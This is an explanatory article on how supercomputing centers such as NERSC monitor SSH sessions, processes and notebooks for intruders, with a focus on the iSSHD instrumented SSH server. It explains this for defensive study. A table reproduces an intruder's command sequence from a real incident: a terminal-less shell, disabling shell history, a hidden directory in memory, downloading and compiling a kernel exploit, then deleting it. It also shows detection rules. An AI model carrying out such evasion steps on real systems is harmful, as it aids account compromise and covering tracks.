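# Host-based security monitoring at national supercomputing centers

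## What a supercomputing center has to watch

A supercomputing center runs very large shared computers, also called high-performance computing (HPC) systems, for researchers who mostly work elsewhere. Each system consists of hundreds or thousands of servers, called nodes, connected by a fast network so they can work on one problem together. The center's security staff keep records of activity on the system and search them for signs of intrusion. Host-based monitoring records what happens inside the machines, including who logged in, which programs ran, and which files those programs opened, while network monitoring records the traffic between machines.

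The National Energy Research Scientific Computing Center (NERSC), at Lawrence Berkeley National Laboratory in California, illustrates the scale. It serves the research programs of the US Department of Energy. According to NERSC's *By the Numbers 2024*, about 11,600 people from some 850 institutions and 46 countries used it that year, on 1,179 projects, and it held 460 petabytes of data. Graduate students made up 32 percent of users and undergraduates 10 percent. NERSC does not employ most of these people or control the laptops they connect from.

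### One job, from login to results

Users normally log in through SSH, an encrypted protocol for running commands remotely. The NERSC documentation page *Establishing Connections* describes the procedure for Perlmutter, the center's supercomputer. The user connects to a single address, and a load balancer passes the connection to one of the login nodes, the shared servers where users edit and compile code and submit jobs. The user then enters a password and a one-time code, or presents a temporary key that removes the need to authenticate again for up to 24 hours. The SSH server can log each connection's account name, time, authentication method and source address.

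*Unveiling User Behavior on Summit Login Nodes as a User* (Wilkinson, Maheshwari and Ferreira da Silva, 2022) reports hourly samples of activity taken over two years on the five login nodes of Summit, a supercomputer at Oak Ridge National Laboratory. The samples included 1,967 users and 9,841 internet addresses. That is about five addresses per user, so a login from an unfamiliar place is weak evidence of anything.

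Next the user edits and compiles a program. Each command starts one or more processes, and several mechanisms can record them. The user's shell usually keeps a history file, but the user can switch it off with one command. Process accounting, an old Unix feature, writes a short record each time a process ends. The Linux audit service, auditd, logs system calls (requests from a program to the kernel, the core of the operating system) and file accesses that an administrator selects in advance. A newer Linux mechanism, eBPF, checks small programs and runs them inside the kernel. Monitoring tools use it to observe events such as program starts and network connections as they happen.

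NERSC's *Basics of Running Jobs* reserves login nodes for editing, compiling and preparing jobs. Users do not always follow such rules. After filtering out legitimate work such as compiling and file compression, Wilkinson and colleagues found that 549 users on Summit, more than a quarter of the total, ran programs that took over 90 percent of a processor. These users ran 495 different programs, most of them for less than an hour. Forty-one users ran such programs without ever submitting a job. Two others periodically restarted their sessions to reset the limits on each login, which let them hold half of the login nodes' graphics processors for about 84 hours. The study does not report any of this as an intrusion, but a detector based only on the official rules would flag much of it as unusual.

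The Summit study's data came from an ordinary account running standard commands that list logged-in users and running processes, so an intruder with any valid account could presumably have collected much the same. The researchers concede that hourly samples miss short events. A command that finishes in ten seconds would nearly always fall between two samples, which is why security staff want a record of every process.

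To run the program at full scale, the user submits a job script to the scheduler, which queues jobs and assigns them to compute nodes, the servers that run them. Users normally reach compute nodes only through the scheduler. Perlmutter has 40 login nodes and 4,864 compute nodes, according to the training course *Running Jobs on Perlmutter* (Tyler, 2023). The course's sample script requests four nodes for eight hours, names the job "science" and launches one program. Slurm, the scheduler at NERSC, returns a job number.

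This step leaves the most orderly trace. SchedMD's *sacct*, the manual page for Slurm's accounting command, lists fields for the user, the times of submission, start and end, the nodes, the working directory, the submitted command line and the exit code. It also lists fields for processor time, memory, and data read and written. But Slurm keeps the job script only if the site has turned that option on. Without the script, the recorded command may be only "sbatch script.sh". The user also chooses the job's name, so a job called "science" could be mining cryptocurrency.

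While the job runs, its owner may want to log in to one of its compute nodes to look at a problem. Sites differ on whether to allow this. NHR@KIT's *Login*, from a German center in Karlsruhe, rules out direct access to compute nodes. Other sites use the Slurm module described in SchedMD's *pam_slurm_adopt*, which refuses an SSH connection from a user who has no job running on that node. If the user has one, the module attaches the new session to it. This links the login to a job number and lets Slurm account for the session's processes and remove them when the job ends.

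Records on a compute node may be short-lived. Many clusters use diskless nodes, which load their operating system over the network at boot and keep nothing on a local disk. Rebooting such a node erases any logs it hasn't sent elsewhere.

Finally, the user moves the results home. NERSC's *Data Transfer Nodes* describes servers for this purpose, each with two 100-gigabit links to the internet and a connection to the shared file systems. The user can copy small files over SSH, which leaves a login entry. For large files, NERSC's *Globus* recommends Globus, a hosted service that manages the transfer, retries failures and reports the status. A network monitor can also record the size and destination of the flow.

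### Four zones and who may enter them

Different nodes on this path are exposed to different people. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) guide *High-Performance Computing Security* (SP 800-223; Guo, Chandramouli and colleagues, 2024) divides an HPC system into four zones by function.

| Zone | What it contains | Who may enter |
|---|---|---|
| Access | Login nodes, data transfer nodes, web portals | Users and administrators, from outside networks, after authentication |
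| Management | Scheduler, configuration servers, system logs | Administrators only, through extra controls; users can send requests to the scheduler |
| High-performance computing | Compute nodes and the fast network between them | Users' jobs, through the scheduler; at some sites, users by SSH |
| Data storage | Parallel file systems and archives | No direct logins for users; they reach files through login nodes, transfer nodes and jobs |

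Only the access zone connects directly to outside networks. Administrators log in there first and then connect to the management zone, for example through a bastion host, a hardened gateway machine. The guide places log storage and alerting in the management zone, so ordinary accounts cannot reach the central log store, the servers where staff collect and search logs from all nodes and turn them into alerts. The guide notes that a site may also forward relevant logs to an analysis system outside the cluster. An intruder who takes over a login node can alter the log files on that node but not the copies already sent elsewhere.

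The boundaries are weaker than they appear in the table. Guo and colleagues warn that root, the administrator account with full control of a machine, on one compute node may amount to root on every system in the HPC zones, depending on the configuration. File permissions are also weak, because each node that mounts a file system enforces them itself. An attacker who can mount the file system from a machine they control can therefore get all the data. So a center has reason to watch for an ordinary account gaining root, even on a node that holds nothing of interest.

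### Why office security does not fit

In an office, the IT department decides which programs employees may run. It can also equip every laptop with a security agent, which is security software that runs continuously on a host. Endpoint detection and response (EDR) products are commercial security agents that record host activity, flag threats and can block them. Several features of a supercomputer make this approach difficult.

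The most basic problem in monitoring a supercomputing center is that outside users bring their own code. Guo and colleagues observe that HPC users regularly modify and recompile their programs, and that their community generally treats slow code as a more urgent problem than published security flaws. A center cannot keep a list of approved programs when every compilation may produce a new one. An unknown program that occupies a thousand nodes is not suspicious in itself either, because the machine is built to run jobs of that size.

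Another difference is that many nodes mount the same file system, so a file written on a login node is immediately available on thousands of compute nodes. This is convenient for researchers, but it also helps an intruder spread a malicious program. Scanning the files for malware is difficult. According to the NIST guide, existing scanners mainly suit single machines, HPC storage can easily exceed a petabyte, and a scan can slow running jobs.

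Supercomputing centers also handle large volumes of legitimate traffic. In May 2026 ESnet, the Department of Energy's research network, reported a test that moved 176 terabytes of data from Marseille to San Diego at nearly 80 gigabits per second. At that rate the transfer takes about five hours. A security team at an ordinary company would probably treat an outflow of that size as a catastrophe, but at a research center it may be simulation output. Conventional firewalls can slow such transfers, so many sites place their transfer nodes in a separate network area without such a firewall.

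Supercomputers are built for speed, and users may accept only security measures that do not noticeably slow their research. Some of the fast hardware also directly interferes with monitoring. When nodes read each other's memory over the network, the exchange can bypass the kernel and its protections, so tools that collect events in the kernel may miss it.

Guo and colleagues note that machines in the access zone work much like enterprise servers and can be hardened with general IT security tools. They advise applying different controls to different types of node. The difficulty is mostly in the compute nodes and storage. Conventional tools fit best on the login nodes, where outsiders first arrive.

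### The intruder with a valid password

In the most common security incident at NERSC, someone uses a valid password or key stolen from its owner. According to NERSC's *Cybersecurity Tutorial*, the attacker typically starts by compromising another computer, perhaps the researcher's own or one at another institution, and installing a program that records keystrokes. When the researcher logs in to the center from that computer, the program records the password. The attacker later uses it to log in as the researcher, from anywhere in the world.

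The attacker then tries to spread. The attacker can read the file where SSH lists the servers the user has visited and try the same credential on each. With root access, the attacker can replace the SSH server with a modified version that captures the passwords of everyone else who logs in. Some of those people have accounts at other centers, so one theft can lead to a series of thefts across institutions.

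At login, this intruder breaks no rule that a machine can check. Any evidence lies in what the person does afterwards, and encryption hid that from network monitors. *NERSC Experiences with Security Tools and Monitoring* (Butler, 2000) describes the center in the middle of this change. In December 1999, after attackers had compromised some accounts with passwords they read off the network, NERSC switched off telnet, an older login protocol that sends everything unencrypted, on its production machines. Its network monitor analyzed telnet sessions among other traffic, but encrypted SSH traffic already made up 7 percent of the volume.

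That monitor was Zeek, an open-source program called Bro until 2018. Zeek turns traffic into events, such as the opening of a connection, and applies rules that the site has written. *Experiences with High Performance Intrusion Detection in the HPC Environment* (Mellander and Campbell, 2011) gives the example of a rule that keeps a list of servers accepting SSH connections and prints a message whenever a new one appears. Each site has to define good and bad traffic itself, because the core of the program has no built-in definition of either.

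With unencrypted logins, staff could apply such rules to the session itself. They could follow the sequence of commands, recover the tools an attacker downloaded, and raise an alert when a command turned off the shell's history file, which Mellander and Campbell treat as a sign of hacker activity. SSH encrypts the session, so a network monitor can still log the two addresses, the timing and the amount of data, but it cannot read the commands. In *Local System Security via SSHD Instrumentation*, Campbell considers this loss well worth accepting because SSH also stopped thieves from reading passwords as they crossed the network. Still, NERSC had about 4,000 users and 52,000 logins a day at the time, and its network monitor could not read the contents of most of those sessions. The traffic is readable only at its two ends, and the center controls one of them, so NERSC modified its own SSH server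 to report session contents to an analyzer.

### No firewall, and a presumption of theft

In 2011, Mellander and Campbell set out the security policy that NERSC had built around this threat. The center assumed that attackers would get hold of reusable credentials, and it relied on rapid response and mitigation rather than restrictions in advance. It reasoned that open science needs users to be as productive as possible, with as few restrictions as possible. It put no firewall in front of its large machines because one would be too restrictive and, at high bandwidth, prohibitive.

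Even under this policy, Zeek worked as a reactive firewall, adding blocks to the router when it detected signs of trouble, and NERSC refused some traffic outright, such as Windows traffic to the supercomputers. Much of this was already in place in 2000, when Butler described administrators and system consoles behind firewalls while the production machines stayed open.

Butler reports that blocking scanners and banning one commonly attacked service cut detected attacks on the network from two or three a week to two or three a month. That is a substantial drop, but it concerns strangers probing from outside. We can infer little from it about intruders who already have a password, and they were the ones who got into user accounts. Mellander and Campbell call the combination of Zeek and the modified SSH server highly effective, but their presentation includes sample alerts and no detection rate.

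NERSC has since begun requiring multi-factor authentication for all users, so a stolen password no longer works without the one-time code. This prevents the simplest form of the attack but probably doesn't eliminate the threat. An intruder who controls a researcher's laptop might copy the temporary key and use it until it expires, and Guo and colleagues still list the hijacking of user sessions among the dangers to the access zone. In a hijacked session, the password, code and source address are all genuine, and only the commands come from the intruder.

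## Recording SSH sessions on the server

An SSH server decrypts what a user types before passing it to the user's shell, and it receives the shell's output before encrypting it. NERSC added code to the server to record this unencrypted text. Staff had worked on the modification for about a year when NERSC announced it in September 2008. They had first installed it on the supercomputer Franklin in June, and by mid-October it was running on four machines, according to NERSC's (2008) notice to users. They called the modified server instrumented SSH, or iSSHD, after sshd, the standard name of the server program.

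### Where the session is readable

The server program runs as a master process that waits for connections and starts a copy of itself for each one. The copy agrees on encryption keys with the user's computer, checks the user's credentials and opens a session. Inside the session, data travels in channels, which are separate streams sharing one network connection. An ordinary shell login needs one channel for the user's input and the shell's output. Forwarding a graphical window or relaying web traffic requires more channels. The encryption covers the connection as a whole, so data inside a channel needs no separate encryption, which Campbell calls the critical point for monitoring.

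Campbell decided where to add code by reading the source of OpenSSH, the free version of SSH that NERSC already used, and running test sessions in debug mode. Campbell chose decision points that most connections passed through, and the ends of code paths where security-relevant information was available. Code at the decision points captures what the user asked for, such as a new session or a tunnel, while code at the ends of paths captures what the server then did, such as starting a shell. Campbell added almost nothing to the key exchange, and for authentication recorded mainly the method and outcome, because ordinary system logs already held the rest.

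According to *Instrumented SSH* (Campbell and Lant, 2009), the modified server had to be as stable and secure as the original, leave the user's experience unchanged and use a negligible share of the machine's resources. To meet these requirements, the team changed as little of OpenSSH as possible, relied on existing programs for everything else, and recruited reviewers from inside and outside NERSC. It also added patches from the Pittsburgh Supercomputing Center that speed up long-distance file transfers, so users also benefited from the change.

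### From a keystroke to an alert

The added code produces events, each of which is a single action or decision, such as a login, a newly opened channel or a line of typing. Events are not marked as good or bad. Every event passes through one function, which takes the event's name, a list of data types and the data. When a channel opens, for example, the function receives the name "channel_new" along with the channel's number, type and label.

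The function writes each event as a line of structured text. It encodes anything the user typed or saw with URL encoding, the scheme that web addresses use for special characters. A space becomes a plus sign, and a control character becomes a percent sign and a code. If a user types "lz", presses backspace and types "s", the function records the input as "lz%7Fs", which preserves the correction. An early version removed control characters, but this lost information and produced confusing text. Encoding also protects analysts, because control characters can change how a terminal behaves, and an intruder might type some in the hope that security staff will later display the log.

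The server then passes the line to stunnel, an existing program that sends it over an encrypted connection to a separate analysis machine. Each line includes a timestamp and identifiers for the host, the connection and the channel, because one tunnel carries the mixed output of many sessions. On the analysis machine, a script writes the lines from all hosts into a single log file. Another program converts the lines into events for Zeek, which applies the site's rules to them as it does to events from network traffic.

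One of the default rules, shown in Campbell's conference slides, raises an alert when a command that a user runs remotely contains "sh -i" or "bash -i", either of which starts an interactive shell. A site can add another shell with one more line in the rule. Because the rules are separate from the SSH server, staff can respond to a new attack without reinstalling software on hundreds of hosts, and they can try a new rule on old logs.

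Some rules raise an alert on a single piece of text that legitimate users almost never produce, such as a phrase from a known attack tool. Others count commands that mean little individually but look suspicious together in one session. Campbell stresses that iSSHD enforces a site's policy and is not designed to react to single anomalies, such as an unexpected sequence of commands. That is probably sensible at a center where legitimate users do many unusual things. An intruder whose commands match no rule therefore raises no alert, though the log still preserves the commands for later investigation.

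### Losing records before interrupting users

According to Mellander and Campbell's slides, NERSC's iSSHD is "designed to lose security data before degrading" the user's experience. A program that writes to a slow or broken connection normally waits until the connection can accept the data. If iSSHD did this, a fault on the analysis machine could freeze the terminals of everyone logged in. The server therefore uses a non-blocking write, which succeeds or fails immediately. After a failure, according to Campbell and Lant, the server logs an error and tries to reconnect to the local stunnel process. If that fails too, it discards the data and the user's session continues normally. Mellander and Campbell add that stunnel has an aggressive timeout, so that data does not pile up on the SSH side.

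The drawback is that an overload or an outage leaves permanent gaps in the record of commands. An intruder who blocked the tunnel could create such a gap deliberately. As a partial safeguard, each master process also sends a regular "heartbeat" event along the same path. If a host's heartbeats stop arriving, staff can tell that something is wrong there.

### How much of a session the server keeps

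iSSHD does not copy everything. A researcher who compiles a large program may fill the screen with thousands of lines that have almost no security value, and a file transfer can run to many gigabytes. All of NERSC's hosts reported to one analysis system. Campbell also borrowed an idea from Time Machine, a network recording system: the data that matters for security tends to come near the beginning of an interactive session. The server therefore stops copying when one side sends a great deal and the other sends little.

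The limits depend on whether the channel has a terminal, the software device that connects an interactive shell to a keyboard and screen. On a terminal channel, the server by default records up to 15 lines or 64 kilobytes of output after each user input, whichever comes first. A matching limit applies to long input without output. If a user types "ls -l" to list a directory, the server keeps the echoed command and the next 14 lines. The count starts again when the user types something else. When the server skips output, it records the number of bytes skipped, which is 31,736 in one sample event in Campbell and Lant's report.

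Channels without a terminal usually carry files or tunneled traffic, but attackers also use them to type commands. On these channels, the server first samples 1,024 bytes. If more than 30 percent of the characters are non-printing, the data is probably a binary file, and the server stops copying it. If the data looks like text, the server keeps copying up to a total of 0.5 megabytes in either direction.

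These limits make the log better evidence of what an intruder attempted than of what the intruder obtained. If someone displays a file of 500 names, the log contains the command and the first few names. A site can change the limits only by recompiling the server.

### A stolen account, command by command

Campbell's paper includes the record of an attack that it calls a textbook case. A user had chosen the same password for NERSC and for another site, which attackers had compromised. One of the attackers logged in to NERSC with the password and entered the following commands.

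| Command | Effect |
|---|---|
| `sh -i`, sent with the login request | Starts an interactive shell without a terminal |
| `uname -a` | Prints the version of the operating system's kernel |
| `unset HISTFILE` | Stops the shell from saving a history of commands |
| `cd /dev/shm`, `mkdir ...`, `cd ...` | Creates and enters a directory named with three dots, in storage held in memory |
| `wget`, with the address of a file `ab.c` | Downloads the source code of a program |
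| `gcc ab.c -o ab -m32` | Compiles it |
| `./ab` | Runs it; it tries to exploit a flaw in the kernel and fails |
| `rm -rf ab ab.c`, `kill -9 $$` | Deletes the program and ends the shell |

A shell without a terminal is the earliest indicator of a possible attack. When a user logs in normally, the system assigns a terminal and makes an entry in its login records. Asking the SSH server to run a shell directly avoids both. Attackers did this often, and Campbell and Lant report that the first version of NERSC's iSSHD did not record such sessions either, so the team had to add support for channels without terminals. They regard the command as suspicious but not as proof of an attack, since what the person types next usually shows whether it is one.

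The next commands quickly showed that the user was an attacker. The user disabled the shell history, which legitimate users very rarely do, and used a directory named with three dots. Unix uses one dot for the current directory and two for the one above it, so three are easy to overlook in a listing, and ordinary listings omit names that begin with a dot anyway. The attacker presumably chose storage in memory because it loses its contents when the machine restarts. The attacker then downloaded, compiled and ran a program. Researchers do that every day, so it would be a weak indicator alone, but this program also printed boastful messages about searching for a target in the kernel. Campbell's default rules include alarms for commands and output of this sort.

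An incident from March 2009 allows a more useful comparison, because Campbell and Lant print the process accounting records beside the alerts. The records list a compiler, a text editor, a directory listing and similar programs that the account's owner could plausibly have run. Zeek's first alert came from the command that disables history. Process accounting doesn't record this command because it is built into the shell and starts no new process. About 15 minutes later, the intruder opened the source code of a known attack tool in the editor, but the accounting records show only that somebody ran an editor. Zeek raised three more alerts when telltale phrases appeared on the screen.

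Two people shared the stolen session through a program that lets several users work in one terminal, and they typed messages to each other at the command prompt. According to Campbell's longer account, they counted 9,787 entries in the machine's table of neighboring addresses, created a new SSH key that would work on every system sharing the home directory, and discussed how to avoid leaving traces. They also checked whether Snort, an intrusion detection program, was running. They logged in to 19 NERSC systems but never gained root. The log preserved the source code of a new tool they had failed to compile, and NERSC added a rule to detect the tool.

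### Results and cost

By 2011 NERSC had run iSSHD in production for nearly three years, on the roughly 350 hosts that handled its 52,000 daily logins. Campbell reports that it had given staff information about roughly three dozen compromised accounts since 2009. In each case they could quickly determine whether the attack had succeeded and recover the tools the attacker had used.

Campbell acknowledges that this evidence is weak. There was no control group, the number of incidents was small, and all of them came from one site, so the results are closer to anecdote than to a test. The three dozen cases are only the ones NERSC knows about, and nobody can say how many intruders it missed. The paper also doesn't give a false alarm rate, which matters a great deal at this scale because one false alarm in every 10,000 logins would produce about five a day, while the real cases came to little more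 than one a month. The best evidence that iSSHD adds something is the March 2009 incident, where the other logs from the same systems showed nothing unusual.

In performance tests, a set of 13 remote commands, including compilation, took an average of 42.78 seconds with the ordinary server and 43.03 seconds with iSSHD, an increase of 0.6 percent. Copying files of around 100 megabytes showed no measurable difference, which the capture limits help explain, since the server copies only the beginning of a large file to the analyzer. Campbell notes that the tests, which used scripts, could have missed small delays in the response to individual keystrokes.

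The system later grew to 400 to 425 hosts, which produced 30 to 50 million log lines a day, according to *Looking for Ghosts in the Machine* (Campbell, 2015). By then Zeek read the log file directly, and NERSC could spread the analysis over several machines. Some form of the code also spread beyond NERSC. The Fedora Project's *gsi openssh* package, a version of OpenSSH for research computing, contains a patch that, according to its notes, came from a Globus patch with "isshd" in its name. This does not show that anyone uses the package to record sessions.

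NERSC probably still runs iSSHD in 2026. In its current notice to users, NERSC describes the system in the present tense and calls the analyzer Zeek, a name the program took in 2018, so someone has revised the text since then. NERSC also states on its general security page that it runs a specialized SSH server for intrusion detection. Neither page has a date, so it is not certain that the system was still in use in 2025 and 2026. The 2011 results are a poor guide to how many intruders the system catches now, because most users then logged in with a password alone.

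### Consent and privacy

Campbell concedes that iSSHD, which copies keystrokes, differs little in principle from the altered SSH servers that attackers have used to steal passwords since at least 1999, except that it collects a wider range of data. The two also differ in who controls the data and whether users know about it.

Campbell's slides list three concerns within NERSC before the system went into service: privacy, whether system administrators and user support staff would accept it, and who would maintain the software in the long run. NERSC found no explicit legal obstacle to intercepting communications on its own systems, but it chose to be completely open about it. Each major staff group could take part in the design and the code review. The center announced the change at user meetings and by email, and made the source code available to anyone interested.

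In the notice, NERSC tells users that it records and analyzes most of their keystrokes and anything its systems display on their screens. If a user connects from NERSC to a computer at another institution, iSSHD records that session as well. NERSC therefore advises users not to connect to other institutions through its machines. The other institution may not know about the recording, and passwords for its systems may end up in NERSC's log.

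Whether to record passwords was the most difficult decision. A recorded password might help in a criminal investigation, but a log full of working passwords is an attractive target for attackers. Campbell let each site choose when compiling the server, so nobody can turn on password recording just by changing a setting. Campbell and Lant describe another option for passwords that users type after logging in. If "Password:" or "Passphrase:" appears on the screen, the server discards whatever the user enters next. The filter misses passwords requested with other prompts, and NERSC warns users that it cannot be fully reliable.

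According to the login banner in Mellander and Campbell's slides, users agree to monitoring by using the systems and have no expectation of privacy. Under its appropriate use policy of January 2019, NERSC monitors the content of all activities on its systems, may keep copies indefinitely, and may share what it finds with law enforcement. Researchers who need the machine can hardly refuse, so their consent mainly shows that they were told about the monitoring. The restrictions on staff may protect users more. Under Berkeley Lab's *Privacy, Monitoring, and Access without Consent* (2021), only the chief information officer, the laboratory director or the deputy director for operations may grant broad authority to monitor content, and employees who do the monitoring must access only the information the task requires.

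The National Center for Supercomputing Applications (NCSA), at the University of Illinois, adopted written rules for the same practice in 2008. *NCSA Security Monitoring Policy* (Slagell, 2008) attributes a quarter of security incidents on the center's HPC systems to compromised user credentials. The policy permits staff to modify secure channels such as SSH to monitor them. NCSA must notify users of the monitoring through agreements, login banners or other means, and must tell them as soon as possible if it detects misuse of their accounts. A version for Blue Waters, then NCSA's large supercomputer, calls for periodic notice of the monitoring.

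Under the policy, NCSA generally discards the detailed SSH logs, which hold most input and output, after about four weeks unless something suspicious has happened. It may keep authentication logs, process accounting and network records for longer. NERSC, by contrast, had years of session data in 2015. Keeping the logs only briefly limits the harm if someone steals or misuses them, but if an intrusion came to light after three months, NCSA's investigators would have no record of the commands.

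Some consent terms are narrower. The San Diego Supercomputer Center's *HPC User Responsibilities* directs monitoring at unauthorized users and warns authorized users that it may also cover their activities. This distinction is hard to apply when credentials are stolen, since staff cannot tell whether a user is authorized until they have looked at the session.

NERSC announced the recording system six months before the March 2009 intrusion, but the announcement did not deter the two intruders or help them avoid being recorded. They discussed their plans in a recorded session and searched only for Snort.

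### Forwarded traffic and intruders with root

Users can send other traffic through an SSH connection, for instance to reach a web page inside the center or to display a graphical window. iSSHD records the request for such a tunnel, with its addresses and ports, but not the contents. In November 2010 some sessions used more than 50 channels, mostly for web browsing. Campbell suggests that some of these users may have been getting around blocks at their own institutions. iSSHD also misses what users type in a terminal window opened through forwarded graphics, because it cannot extract the keystrokes from the graphics data. In 2011 Campbell listed both problems as future work.

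An intruder who gains root on a login node could also replace the SSH server or stop stunnel, and users would notice nothing because the writes are non-blocking. If the intruder typed the commands leading up to root access in a monitored session, they would already be on the analysis machine. iSSHD is therefore most useful in the minutes before an attack on the kernel succeeds.

Multi-factor authentication has made session hijacking more attractive. An attacker with root on the researcher's own computer can insert commands into a session the researcher has opened. iSSHD would record these commands like any others, and a rule might match them. *Network Detection of Interactive SSH Impostors Using Deep Learning* (Piet, Sharma and colleagues, 2023) describes an attempt to recognize impostors by the timing and size of the packets a client sends, which reflect how a person types. The method does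 not need the session's contents, so it would also ease the privacy problem. But it depends on someone typing, so it seems unlikely to help against commands that a program inserts.

Even a complete session log contains only what the user typed and what appeared on the screen. A script with a harmless-looking name can run any number of programs without displaying anything. Campbell planned to connect the sessions to process accounting to see which programs had run. By 2015, NERSC was also feeding auditd records into Zeek.

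### Notebooks and web portals

A growing share of work bypasses the SSH server. Jupyter is free software for writing and running code in a web browser, in documents called notebooks. A background process called a kernel, unrelated to the operating system kernel, runs the code and returns the results. JupyterHub starts and manages notebooks for many users. *Delivering Science as a Service* (2026) demonstrates a setup at NERSC in which the user logs in on a web page instead of through SSH and receives a notebook with graphics processors on Perlmutter. Jupyter also provides a file browser and a command-line terminal, so someone with a stolen credential could do much of what the attackers in Campbell's examples did without iSSHD recording any of it.

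The San Diego Supercomputer Center had a different version of the problem. Thomas, Kandes and colleagues (2025) explain in *The SDSC Satellite Reverse Proxy Service for Launching Secure Jupyter Notebooks* that the center's policies did not allow JupyterHub to run as root on a login node with thousands of accounts. Users started their own notebooks instead, often on the login nodes and with the default settings, which send everything unencrypted. They were also careless with the notebook's web address. The center regarded each notebook as "a backdoor into the user's account", because anyone with the address and the notebook's password could run code as that user.

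Staff first encouraged users to set up encryption themselves, with their own certificates or through an SSH tunnel. Many found this too difficult and carried on as before. Since fall 2020 the center has offered a proxy, a server that sits between the browser and the notebook. A script obtains a random-looking web address and submits a job to the scheduler. When the job starts on a compute node, it sends the proxy the notebook's location, and the proxy connects the browser to the notebook. The address stops working after a set time, which cannot exceed the maximum length of a job.

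This arrangement protects the traffic on the public internet. Thomas and colleagues do not present it as a monitoring system, but the proxy decrypts the traffic from the browser and forwards it unencrypted over the cluster's internal network, where a network monitor could in principle read it. By contrast, iSSHD records that a user opened an SSH tunnel but not the traffic that passes through it.

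Reading notebook traffic is still harder than reading a terminal session. Jupyter exchanges messages over WebSocket, a protocol that keeps a two-way connection open between a browser and a server. *Jupyter Notebook Attacks Taxonomy* (2024), a paper from NCSA, describes encrypted WebSocket traffic as a challenge even for Zeek, and reports that nobody had developed a security monitoring architecture specifically for Jupyter. Jupyter's own logs are mainly for diagnosing faults and tracking usability. Zeek now has a WebSocket analyzer and a log for these connections, but these help only where the monitor receives decrypted traffic.

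The NCSA paper proposes recording Jupyter activity at the end where it is readable, as NERSC did for SSH. Developers would build a tracing tool into the Jupyter kernel, starting with the Python kernel, to log the user's commands. The paper names NERSC's instrumented SSH as a possible guide to the design. It does not specify how the tool would be protected from tampering. A notebook's kernel normally runs under the user's own account, so an intruder in that account may be able to alter or bypass the tool, whereas the SSH server has privileges that the user lacks.

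Administrators have asked for something similar for Jupyter notebooks. In *Implementing Audit Logging?*, a thread on the Jupyter project's forum, one participant finds no ready way to log the code that users run in notebooks under JupyterHub. Another suggests auditd, but the first wants to log Python commands, such as a query on a table of data. A query on data already in memory may produce no system call that identifies it, in which case auditd would miss it. The operating system can still record when a notebook starts another program or opens a file, whether the user connected through SSH or a browser.

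## Recording commands and processes on login nodes

A session log shows that a user ran `./build.sh` but not which programs the script started. The kernel can supply that information, because a process has to make a system call to run a program. Centers can collect it on login nodes in several ways, which differ in how much detail they keep and who can suppress them.

### Shell history and process accounting

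The simplest record is the shell's history file, which keeps the full text of commands typed at a prompt. It leaves out the programs that scripts run, and it belongs to the user, who can edit or delete it. An intruder can also use it to find other servers. *Intrusion Detection* (Brillault, 2013), a set of training slides from the physics laboratory CERN, describes an intruder who logs in to a stolen account, searches the history file for "ssh", connects to another server and repeats the procedure there.

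Process accounting is harder to avoid because the kernel writes the records. *NVision-PA*, an NCSA paper by Ermopoulos and Yurcik, describes records of only 32 bytes each. Each record holds the user and group, the first eight characters of the command's name, the time the process ended, the time and memory it used, the disk blocks it read or wrote, and a flag if it ran as root. Current Linux versions keep up to 15 characters of the name. Centers also use these records to bill users for processor time.

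The record does not include command-line arguments. If an intruder copies a file with `scp`, investigators learn that the account ran `scp` and when it finished, but not which file it copied or where the file went. The recorded name can also be misleading, since a user can run a malicious tool through a link with an innocent name. And because the kernel writes the record only when the process ends, a password-cracking program that runs for a week does not appear in the log until it finishes.

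### What auditd records about one command

Auditd can record the arguments as well, and it does so when the program starts. Velociraptor's *Linux.Events.ProcessExecutions*, part of an open-source tool for investigating compromised machines, installs this rule:

`auditctl -a exit,always -F arch=b64 -S execve -k procmon`

The system call `execve` loads and runs a program. The rule makes the kernel report every such call when it finishes and attach the label "procmon" so that staff can search for it. The condition `arch=b64` limits the rule to 64-bit calls, so a site needs a second rule for 32-bit calls. Without it, a 32-bit program could start others without leaving a record. The attacker in Campbell's textbook case compiled the attack program with `-m32`, which produces a 32-bit program.

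One short command yields several records. Campbell, in *Open Science, Open Security*, prints the result for `uname -m`, which displays the machine's processor type.

| Record | Contents |
|---|---|
| SYSCALL | The call `execve`, the program `/bin/uname`, the process and its parent, the terminal, the user's identities, and whether the call succeeded |
| EXECVE | The two parts of the command, `uname` and `-m` |
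| CWD | The directory in which the user ran it |
| PATH | The file `/bin/uname`, with its owner and permissions |
| PATH | A second file owned by root, probably the loader that starts programs |

Linux keeps several user identities for each process, and most of them change if the user becomes root. The login identity, which the system assigns at login, stays the same. So if an intruder takes over a physicist's account and then gains root, later records still identify the physicist's account.

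Auditd still misses some activity. Like process accounting, it does not record `unset HISTFILE`. If someone runs a Python script, the rule records `python script.py` but nothing the script does internally. Other rules can record the files the script opens or the connections it makes, but they generate more data.

### How a compilation floods the log

The execution rule alone produces enough data to cause problems. Suppose a researcher compiles a program with 10,000 source files, and the build starts a shell, a compiler driver, the compiler itself and an assembler for each file. That makes 40,000 program starts and, at five records each, 200,000 audit records. A parallel build on a large login node can produce them within minutes. The kernel holds records in a queue of limited size until auditd collects them. When the queue is full, the kernel may delay the programs that produce the records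 or discard records, depending on its settings. One user's compilation on a login node can therefore slow down other people's work or cause the records of an intruder's commands to be lost.

Campbell therefore chose a limited set of system calls at NERSC, covering changes of privilege, network activity and changes to sensitive files. In initial tests, the overhead for an average user's activity was about 0.5 percent. An audit event can consist of up to ten records with 10 to 30 fields each, so NERSC wrote software to combine these into a single line before analysis in Zeek. Bengen's *Linux Audit* describes LAUREL, a newer add-on also meant to make audit logs easier to use.

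The official security guide for TOSS, the Linux system that Livermore, Los Alamos and Sandia national laboratories share, is more selective. The rules in STIG Viewer's *The TOSS audit system must prevent all software from executing at higher* (2026) record an execution only if the program gains root's user or group identity and the user who started it has a different one. This happens when an ordinary user starts a program such as `sudo`, which the system allows to run as root. Compiling software produces almost no such events. But an attack on the kernel often changes all of a process's identities to root before it opens a shell. The identities then match, so these rules would probably not record the shell.

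Auditd remains a standard choice. *DenyRoot* (2026), a presentation from the Swiss national supercomputing center (CSCS), lists it alongside eBPF as a source of information about users' applications.

### osquery and command-logging modules

Osquery, a free program that Facebook released in 2014, presents the state of a machine as database tables. Staff can query these to see which processes are running under an account, or which programs are waiting for network connections. Each result is a snapshot, so it misses commands that start and finish between queries, as the hourly samples on Summit did. Osquery can also record program starts continuously, but on Linux it gets them from eBPF or from the same kernel audit system that auditd uses. It is more convenient than the other tools but adds little evidence that they cannot collect.

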